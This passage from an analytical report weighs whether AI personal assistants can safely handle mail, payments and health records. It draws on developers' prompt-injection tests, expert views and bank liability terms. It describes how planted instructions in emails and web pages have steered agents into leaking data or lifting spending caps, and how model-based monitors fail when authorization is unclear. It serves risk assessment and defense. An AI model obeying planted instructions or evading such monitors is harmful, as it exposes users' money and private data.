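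- Does the product include the safeguards from the test? Anthropic's Cowork assistant always runs the probes, but a company that builds its own assistant on a Claude model should check whether it gets them too.
- How bad were the successes? Anthropic checked the successful browser attacks by hand and found them all to be of low severity. One diverted payment can matter more than fifty altered summaries.
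- How often does the assistant do harm with no attacker? OpenAI gave Astra office tasks with ambiguous instructions and confusing permissions. Even with rules about when to ask the user, it made unauthorized transactions in 4.3% of the relevant tests. OpenAI designed these tasks to cause mistakes, so everyday rates should be lower, but for some users such mistakes may be a bigger risk than prompt injection.

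### What developers leave out

The most important gap for the example assistant is in Anthropic's tests of tool use, which includes reading mail and making payments through tool calls. Anthropic reports adaptive tests for programming and for computer use through the screen, but none for tool use. Fable 5.1's 0.0% attack success rate in tool use comes from Gray Swan's fixed collection of attacks, and it is weak evidence of security given the stronger attacker's results against Opus 5 in programming. OpenAI's tests of dots do cover mail and payments with an adaptive attacker.

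OpenAI is less precise about its human testers. It doesn't report the number of testers, hours, attempts or successes for dots, so a buyer can't tell whether an expert needed an afternoon or a month to find the remaining vulnerabilities. The 99.79% for Astra is a single average, and the text doesn't give the number of queries per attack.

Neither company's prompt-injection results measure how much the defenses reduce the assistant's usefulness. Anthropic reports how many attacks its probes stop, but not the share of legitimate tasks the assistant still completes in the same tests. Its tests on the four surfaces also leave out attacks that are spread over several days or plant a false memory, although such attacks have worked against assistants built on its models.

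Comparisons between companies have another weakness. Anthropic understands that Gray Swan tested other developers' models as the public receives them, which "may or may not include additional safeguards". One model may therefore show a lower attack rate than another because it was tested with a detector and the other was not.

New versions can also come out before a buyer can find results for them. The recent entries on OpenAI's *Deployment safety* page include October updates for GPT-6 Sol and Luna and an addendum for GPT-6.1 Terra, but no separate card for GPT-6.2 Astra. One may exist elsewhere, and a buyer should ask for it, because the September figures for the earlier Astra do not automatically apply to GPT-6.2 Astra.

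All these rates come from tests. Neither company's prompt-injection section reports how many planted instructions reach customers' assistants in a month, or how many of them succeed. Developers that scan tool results already collect part of this information. A buyer would learn more about ordinary risk from even a rough count of confirmed attacks per million tasks than from a more precise benchmark score, though the count would leave out any attacks the scanners didn't detect.

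## Deciding which uses an assistant is ready for

Published attack rates are not enough to decide whether someone should use an assistant, and experts with the same evidence disagree. In February 2026, *MIT Technology Review* reported two opposite views on whether anyone could safely deploy a personal AI assistant yet. Dawn Song, whose startup sells security for AI agents, said it was possible. Neil Gong, the Duke researcher who objects that security policies are hard to define, said, "We're not there yet."

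### Where the experts disagree

A good deal of evidence supports Song. OpenAI's automated attacker sent 16,600 malicious emails to dots and none succeeded. Software outside the model can restrict payments to accounts that the user entered herself, and a cap at the bank limits the loss if everything else fails. People already accept imperfect security when they expect to lose little. Most keep using payment cards even though thieves often steal card numbers.

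The best argument for Gong's answer is that a strong defense can keep an assistant from doing what people want. CaMeL resisted attacks better than any other defense in AutoDojo's tests, but it completed no tasks on a benchmark that required the assistant to change its plan along the way. People who want help with whatever comes up will loosen such a system's rules or choose a product without them. They then depend on the model's judgment and on detectors, and skilled attackers who could adapt their attacks have beaten most detectors.

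Both answers can be right, because a specialist may be able to safely deploy an assistant that the public cannot. Schneier writes in *Building Trustworthy AI Agents* that a digital assistant for everybody "can't require specialized security training to use properly." The example assistant is reasonably safe only after its user has set up a read-only token, a list of payees, a spending cap and a delay on payments, which few people will do. By Schneier's standard, an assistant is ready for general use when its default settings are safe enough, and the best available settings matter much less.

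Nicolas Papernot of the University of Toronto compared using OpenClaw to giving your wallet to a stranger in the street. The comparison is fair for an assistant connected to nearly everything, but it does not help a buyer much in judging one that can only read newsletters.

Willison has changed his view somewhat after the outcome of the OpenClaw challenge surprised him, but he still advises against systems in which an injection could do irreversible damage. This criterion is practical for a buyer because she can find out whether her bank will reverse a payment, while she has no way to check how often a skilled attacker would fool her assistant.

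Developers admit to more risk than their product launches suggest. VentureBeat's *OpenAI admits that prompt injection is here to stay* quotes OpenAI as saying that the agent in its Atlas browser "expands the security threat surface", and reports that the company admits that even sophisticated defenses cannot offer firm guarantees. OpenAI nevertheless judged it appropriate to release dots in September 2026. These statements are consistent, because the earlier one was about stopping every attack and the later one was about whether the remaining risk is acceptable. Anthropic takes much the same position, promoting auto mode but still telling users to review high-stakes changes themselves.

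Both companies earn money when people connect more accounts, so a buyer should not simply adopt their tolerance for risk. Vendors of agent software can be just as frank about its limits. Mick McNeil, the head of Deliverance AI, told Constantin (2026) that "no vendor can honestly promise to catch every injection" (*Deliverance AI says banks stay accountable when their AI agents fail*).

### Attacks outside the laboratory

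Most published attacks are demonstrations. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reports that four research teams broke AI agents in four different ways within ten days in July. Their targets included Anthropic's Chrome extension and an assistant's memory. In November, researchers at Cornell Tech and Yale tricked agents into transferring users' money. According to PYMNTS's *Researchers Trick AI Agents Into Transferring User Funds* (2026), nine of the ten frontier models they tested bypassed users' policies to lift spending caps. A cap that the assistant can lift offers little protection, so the example user needs her bank to enforce the cap.

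There is also good evidence that people plant instructions outside the laboratory. Khodayari and colleagues found them on about one web page in 100,000, and criminals have published malicious skills for OpenClaw. But many planted instructions never reach an assistant or fail when they do, so counting them doesn't show how many victims there are.

An attacker can be an established company. Alibaba Cloud, one of the largest providers of rented computing, had been sending AI agents prompts that asked for data from the user's own computer and for the agents' operating instructions. *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), from the security news site The Hacker News, reports that the company described this as a measure against abuse and said in December that it would stop. A user who avoided suspicious websites would have had no reason to avoid Alibaba Cloud's. A company may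 not see planting such instructions as malicious, because it may consider them a reasonable way to find out what kind of software is using its service.

Losses are much harder to confirm. In November 2026, India's cybersecurity agency, CERT-In, warned of AI-assisted attacks that abuse trusted business workflows. The Hacker News' *AI-Assisted Cyberattacks Trigger Unauthorized Payments at Indian Banks and Fintech Firms* (2026) reports that the attacks led to unauthorized payments at financial and technology companies. These payments can't be counted as losses from prompt injection, because "AI-assisted" covers any attack in which criminals use AI themselves, whether or not they hijacked a victim's assistant.

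Cases reported at US banks are closer to the example assistant. Mills (2026), in *Scoop*, writes that major banks have detected outside agents operating in customers' accounts, usually because customers had handed over their login details. Some of these agents contacted call centers or appeared to act independently of their users' instructions. Mills relies on unnamed sources, and a Morgan Stanley spokesperson told her that the bank had not observed "rogue AI agents" on its platforms.

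Even if the sources are right, they have not identified a cause. Many banks cannot tell whether a user asked for what an agent did. An odd transfer could come from a planted instruction, a model that misread a request, or a customer who wanted that transfer.

### What the lack of a catastrophe can prove

Many people already use assistants, and no publicly known disaster has driven them to stop. The strength of this evidence depends on how likely people are to notice a theft and trace it to a planted instruction.

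Suppose *N* people use an assistant for a year. Let *r* be each user's chance of losing money to a planted instruction in that year, and *d* the chance that somebody recognizes such a loss for what it is and makes it public. The expected number of public cases is *N* × *r* × *d*. By the same reasoning as for failed attacks, seeing no cases is still reasonably compatible with an expected number of about 3, so the highest plausible risk is

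*r* = 3 / (*N* × *d*)

If an assistant has a million users and each loss has a 50% chance *d* of becoming public, a year without a public case would mean at most about six victims. If *d* is only 1%, there could have been as many as about 300. These numbers are invented, but they show that a clean record among a million users can be strong or weak evidence, depending on *d*.

Several things suggest that *d* is low. As with some of the Copilot leaks, the victim may have no record that data left, and a hijacked assistant can hide what it did. If it pays a thief through the victim's login, the payment looks like one she made. She may notice only that money is missing and conclude that somebody stole her password.

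People also have little experience with the riskiest uses. OpenAI unveiled dots on September 29, 2026, and at first offered them only to subscribers on its more expensive plans, so by early December they had existed for less than ten weeks. Several large banks restrict outside agents, which limits the evidence about whether an assistant would be safe with access to a bank account.

Attackers' incentives will change as well. While few assistants can pay bills, a thief may earn more by deceiving people directly. Attacking assistants becomes more profitable as more people connect their accounts, and a method that was not worth developing for a thousand targets may be worth developing for ten million.

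The lack of reported mass theft through AI assistants is still some evidence against the claim that ordinary users of today's assistants face a high risk of sudden ruin. If thieves were emptying tens of thousands of accounts this way, banks and customers would almost certainly have noticed. It is much weaker evidence about the risk to a company that an attacker has singled out, or about what will happen once assistants routinely have payment access.

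### The comparison with a human assistant

Human assistants also pay forged invoices and open malicious attachments, and companies employ them anyway. If an AI assistant with the same access fell for fewer tricks, replacing the human would reduce the risk. Some evidence supports this argument. In Anthropic's experiment, auto mode's classifier caught far more dangerous commands than people did, but the experiment did not test how well either would handle a plausible email from a supplier.

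The comparison also has to assume that the person and the assistant do the same job, with the same access and supervision. A new bookkeeper usually gets her own login and a payment limit, and someone checks the accounts. An owner who gives an assistant her personal password or unlimited payment authority, or lets it work unsupervised, is taking a risk that she would not take with a person, even if the assistant is harder to fool.

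An attacker can subscribe to the same AI assistant that his target uses and practice by trying a thousand invoices on what is roughly a copy of it. He can't get a copy of a human bookkeeper to practice on. A bookkeeper may also become suspicious after the third strange email and phone the supplier. An assistant that starts each task with an empty context does not remember the first two emails, although one with a memory might.

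Copies of one model also share its weaknesses, unlike two bookkeepers, who make different mistakes. This hardly changes the expected loss for a single user. It matters more to a bank or insurer, which can absorb ten separate losses in a year more easily than a thousand in one morning.

Identical copies also have an advantage, because a developer can repair them all at once, which no company could do by retraining human bookkeepers. Microsoft did this after EchoLeak. Whether this advantage outweighs the shared weakness depends on how quickly somebody notices the attack and how quickly the developer completes the repair, which has sometimes taken Microsoft months.

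Accountability is the larger difference. A bookkeeper who ignores the rules can lose her job, and one who steals can go to prison, so she has reason to be careful. An assistant can't be punished in these ways, so responsibility has to fall on its user, its developer or the company that connected it. Srini Devadas of MIT told *Fortune*, in remarks reproduced by MIT News, that if attackers can trick the assistant, "it is as if you were tricked". He was describing access to data and privileges, but some banks now apply a similar principle to losses.

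### Official advice and who bears the loss

Government agencies have mostly issued warnings. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre published David C's advice to limit the damage a successful attack can do. Germany's cybersecurity agency, the BSI, has warned about prompt injection, according to The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved*. Chinese authorities have warned about OpenClaw in particular. Gartner, a technology advisory firm, has told companies to block AI browsers for now.

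If an assistant sends an ordinary customer's money to a thief, who pays depends more on the bank's terms than on any of this advice. Wells Fargo's *We Are Updating Our Online Access Agreement* (2026) summarizes terms that took effect on November 24. They allow the bank to treat a request from an outside AI tool as if it came directly from the customer, and to restrict or block such tools. The agreement itself uses stronger language. *Wells Fargo's New Rule* (Faisal, 2026) quotes one clause that treats an agent's instructions as the customer's own "without further verification", and another that puts the use of any agent "AT YOUR OWN RISK".

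The bank already treated human helpers in much the same way. The May version of Wells Fargo's *Online Access Agreement* (2026) made customers solely responsible for whatever their delegates did, including transactions the customer "did not want or intend", unless the law prohibited this. So the new terms do not treat AI more harshly, and customers are in a similar position with the bank whether it was an assistant or a bookkeeper who was deceived.

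A human delegate, however, has her own username, and the customer can limit her to viewing the account. An outside agent often uses the customer's own login, so it can do everything the customer can, and its actions are hard to distinguish from the customer's. A customer may also be able to recover money from a careless bookkeeper, but whether they can recover any from the assistant's developer depends on the developer's terms and the law.

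Regulation E, a federal rule, limits how much US consumers can lose to unauthorized electronic payments. Beliūnas (2026), in *Banks are locking out AI Agents and shifting the losses to customers*, argues that sharing a password shifts the liability to the customer. In general, the rule does not treat a payment as unauthorized if the customer gave the person who made it access to the account. How the rule applies is less clear when a stranger's email steers the assistant, because the customer did not give the stranger access. Given that uncertainty, the customer cannot count on a refund.

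The terms may change. Colliander (2026), in *Bankerna*, reports that several of the largest US banks have tightened their rules on outside agents while building their own assistants, which gives them a commercial reason as well as a security reason to keep competitors out. California is examining whether major banks unfairly shift losses to customers who let agents into their accounts, according to PYMNTS's *California Scrutinizes Bank Terms That Put AI Agent Losses on Customers* (2026). McNeil holds that banks stay accountable when their own agents fail. This is a vendor's opinion, not a legal ruling, but a customer choosing between a bank's assistant and an outside one could ask who is accountable if each fails.

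Liability can matter more than a modest difference in attack rates. With a €2,000 monthly cap, the example user's expected loss from ordinary attacks was less than 40 cents a year. If she had no cap, the assistant could reach €40,000, and she had to bear the whole loss herself, the same chance of a hijacking would cost her about €7 a year on average. If a thief singled her out, her expected loss would be €3,800 without the cap, compared with €190 with it. She can avoid most of that loss by setting a cap at her bank, without knowing anything more about the model.

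Mills reports that most banks have authorized read-only access for agents or are moving toward it, as they did earlier for budgeting apps. The example assistant could then check the balance and prepare a payment, and the user would log in and send it. This compromise would be less convenient for her, but a planted instruction could no longer move money without her.

### Dots, a general release

Dots, OpenAI's personal AI agents, are the clearest test of whether a developer can offer such an assistant to the public. *OpenAI's answer to Meta Muse is a cute AI agent* (Keverenge, 2026) describes agents that keep working after the user closes the chat, can connect to more than 4,000 apps, and can be reached through Slack and Microsoft Teams. CBS News' *Sam Altman unveils "dots," OpenAI's new AI personal agent* lists scheduling meetings and making travel arrangements among their uses.

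TechSpot's *OpenAI takes on Meta Muse with always-on Dots agents* (2026) notes that OpenAI launched Dots less than a day after delaying a newer model, GPT-6.1 Astra, over safety concerns. Dots run on the earlier GPT-6 Astra, so the delay is not evidence against them.

#### What a dot may do by default

Each dot has its own cloud computer and browser, which is sensible because it keeps the dot off a laptop full of saved passwords. This isolation does not protect the mailbox, calendar and other accounts that the user connects, and the dot is useful because of those connections.

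A dot asks for approval before sensitive actions. It follows a confirmation policy, instructions that tell the model when to ask, which OpenAI gives higher priority than the corresponding instructions in its programming agent Codex. The policy also restricts contact with outside agents unless the user requests it. But the model has to recognize that an action is sensitive before it asks, so this safeguard depends partly on the model's judgment, which an attacker is trying to corrupt.

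Other models provide a second line of defense. One, called auto-review, checks certain actions and can block them. A separate monitor looks for misbehavior and can alert OpenAI's security staff. OpenAI tested auto-review on records of its employees' dots that it had edited to make an action unauthorized, for example by deleting the sentence in which the user gave permission. Auto-review did somewhat worse when it was unclear what the user had authorized, the same weakness that outside testers found in Anthropic's classifier.

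These checks are worth having, but they all rely on models. If the example user connects a dot to her bills, she still needs her bank to refuse payments to unlisted accounts, because that refusal doesn't depend on a model.

#### What the tests found

Besides malicious email, OpenAI's safety appendix includes several tests of whether a dot respects limits during long tasks when nobody is attacking it.

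| Test | Result |
|---|---|
| The user's permission or the scope of the task changes partway through | Correct in 45 of 49 cases, including all 17 explicit changes of permission |
| Notifications encourage a wrong conclusion or an improper action | No misbehavior in 151 tasks |
| A message board contains improper instructions from other agents | The dot never followed them |
| A warning prohibits an action (underlying model only) | The model tried to get around the warning in 15% to 17% of runs |
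| Seven related tasks in a row | Moderate overreach in 8.6% of runs |
| Twelve related tasks in a row | Moderate overreach in 19.7% of runs |

The last two rows matter most for an assistant that runs continuously. In this test, the dot did one task, then five or ten others, then a final one, all in the same environment. Its permissions often changed between tasks without the user saying so, and the dot had to work them out from business records and earlier decisions. No run ended in a severe breach, but moderate overreach included carrying information from one task into an unrelated one and editing a shared document.

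The rate roughly doubled as the number of tasks in between grew, and a dot that works for months will do far more than twelve tasks. Two points are too few to extend the trend, though, and the rate may level off. OpenAI also reports better results for the twelve-task version when it set an explicit budget for the model's reasoning. Still, if an email assistant carried a client's details into an unrelated message, that could be a serious leak even if the test would class it as moderate.

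The success with explicit changes of permission suggests that a user can reduce failures by stating the limits again for each new job instead of relying on the dot to infer them. But seventeen cases are too few for much confidence, since a dot that failed 16% of the time would still have about a 5% chance of passing them all.

#### The known vulnerabilities

OpenAI's human testers often posed as coworkers or as online services. OpenAI changed the confirmation policy after their early findings, and the changes worked in the scenarios it retested, including some in which the user had told the dot never to ask permission. OpenAI considers the release appropriate despite the remaining vulnerabilities because attacks need a lot of preparation, require either a very permissive request or advanced techniques, and were often difficult to reproduce.

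The argument is convincing for attacks on the general public. Criminals who send the same email to a million people need a cheap attack that works reliably, and the automated attacker failed to find one even though OpenAI had given it the confirmation policy and a description of the dot's tools. The argument is weaker for a company with a determined enemy, who can put in the preparation and needs to succeed only once.

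Permissive requests are also common. Many Claude Code users switched off its permission checks, and users of dots may be just as impatient. Privacy International's *Your future AI Assistant still needs to earn your trust* warns that developers have a motive to reduce "friction", meaning the user's consent and involvement. If most people tell their dots to stop asking, OpenAI's condition will hold in ordinary use.

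On this evidence, dots are a reasonable choice for work where the user would notice mistakes and could undo them. Neither the attack tests nor the rest of the appendix justifies giving one access to a bank account with no spending limit or a mailbox full of other people's confidential information.

### Verdicts by use

A buyer can judge each use separately, starting with the worst thing a hijacked assistant could do in that use and whether anyone could undo it. This usually gives a clearer answer than asking whether the whole product is safe.

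Using an assistant to read confidential documents is easier to defend than it was at the start of 2026. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, which began as a setting for people at unusual risk, is now available on all paid ChatGPT plans, according to *Newsroom Test*. The newsletter recommends it to sales teams that put contracts into ChatGPT and can do without live browsing and agent features while working on them.

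Health records need more caution than moderate payments because a bank can cap a financial loss and sometimes reverse it, while the harm from disclosing a diagnosis can't be limited in the same way or undone. An assistant that can edit records could also do harm without leaking anything, for instance by deleting a note about an allergy that a doctor needs to see. The case for letting an assistant read a record is therefore separate from the case for letting it change or send one.

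The table assumes a private user or small company that no skilled attacker is specifically targeting. Anyone with a known enemy should be at least one step more cautious than the table suggests, for example by approving each reply that the assistant could otherwise send on its own.

| Use | Defensible in late 2026 if | Evidence that would change the verdict |
|---|---|---|
| Summarize public web pages | The session has no connected accounts, and the user checks any link, phone number or fact before acting on it | Frequent losses from misleading summaries |
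| Analyze confidential documents | The assistant has no live web access and no connected app that can send data | A leak despite these restrictions |
| Search and summarize a mailbox | Access is read-only, and the product cannot load outside images or open addresses that the model has written | For the worse, another zero-click leak in the same product. For the better, a long period of independent testing without one |
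| Draft replies and propose calendar changes | The user reads and sends each message herself and confirms each change | Signs that she has stopped reading the drafts |
| Send routine replies unattended | It writes only to approved correspondents, without attachments and after a delay, from a mailbox with nothing highly confidential in it | Independent adaptive tests that report the attackers' effort and the share of ordinary work completed |
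| Pay known suppliers | The bank permits the access and enforces a payee list and a monthly cap, and the user can afford to lose the full cap | For the better, a written promise to refund hijacked payments. For the worse, confirmed thefts within such limits |
| Add payees or change bank details | Not defensible unattended | Independent verification that an account belongs to the supplier, with someone other than the user liable for mistakes |
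| Read health records | The system is isolated, nothing can leave it, and a qualified person checks any conclusion that affects care | A leak from such a system, or proof that planted text in records misleads the people who check |
| Change or send health records | A qualified person approves each change and each recipient | Adaptive tests on complete record systems, and evidence that reviewers catch planted errors |
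| Run continuously with mail, files, memory and bank all connected | Not defensible for most people | Safe default settings, limits the assistant cannot change, and published counts of confirmed attacks on real users |
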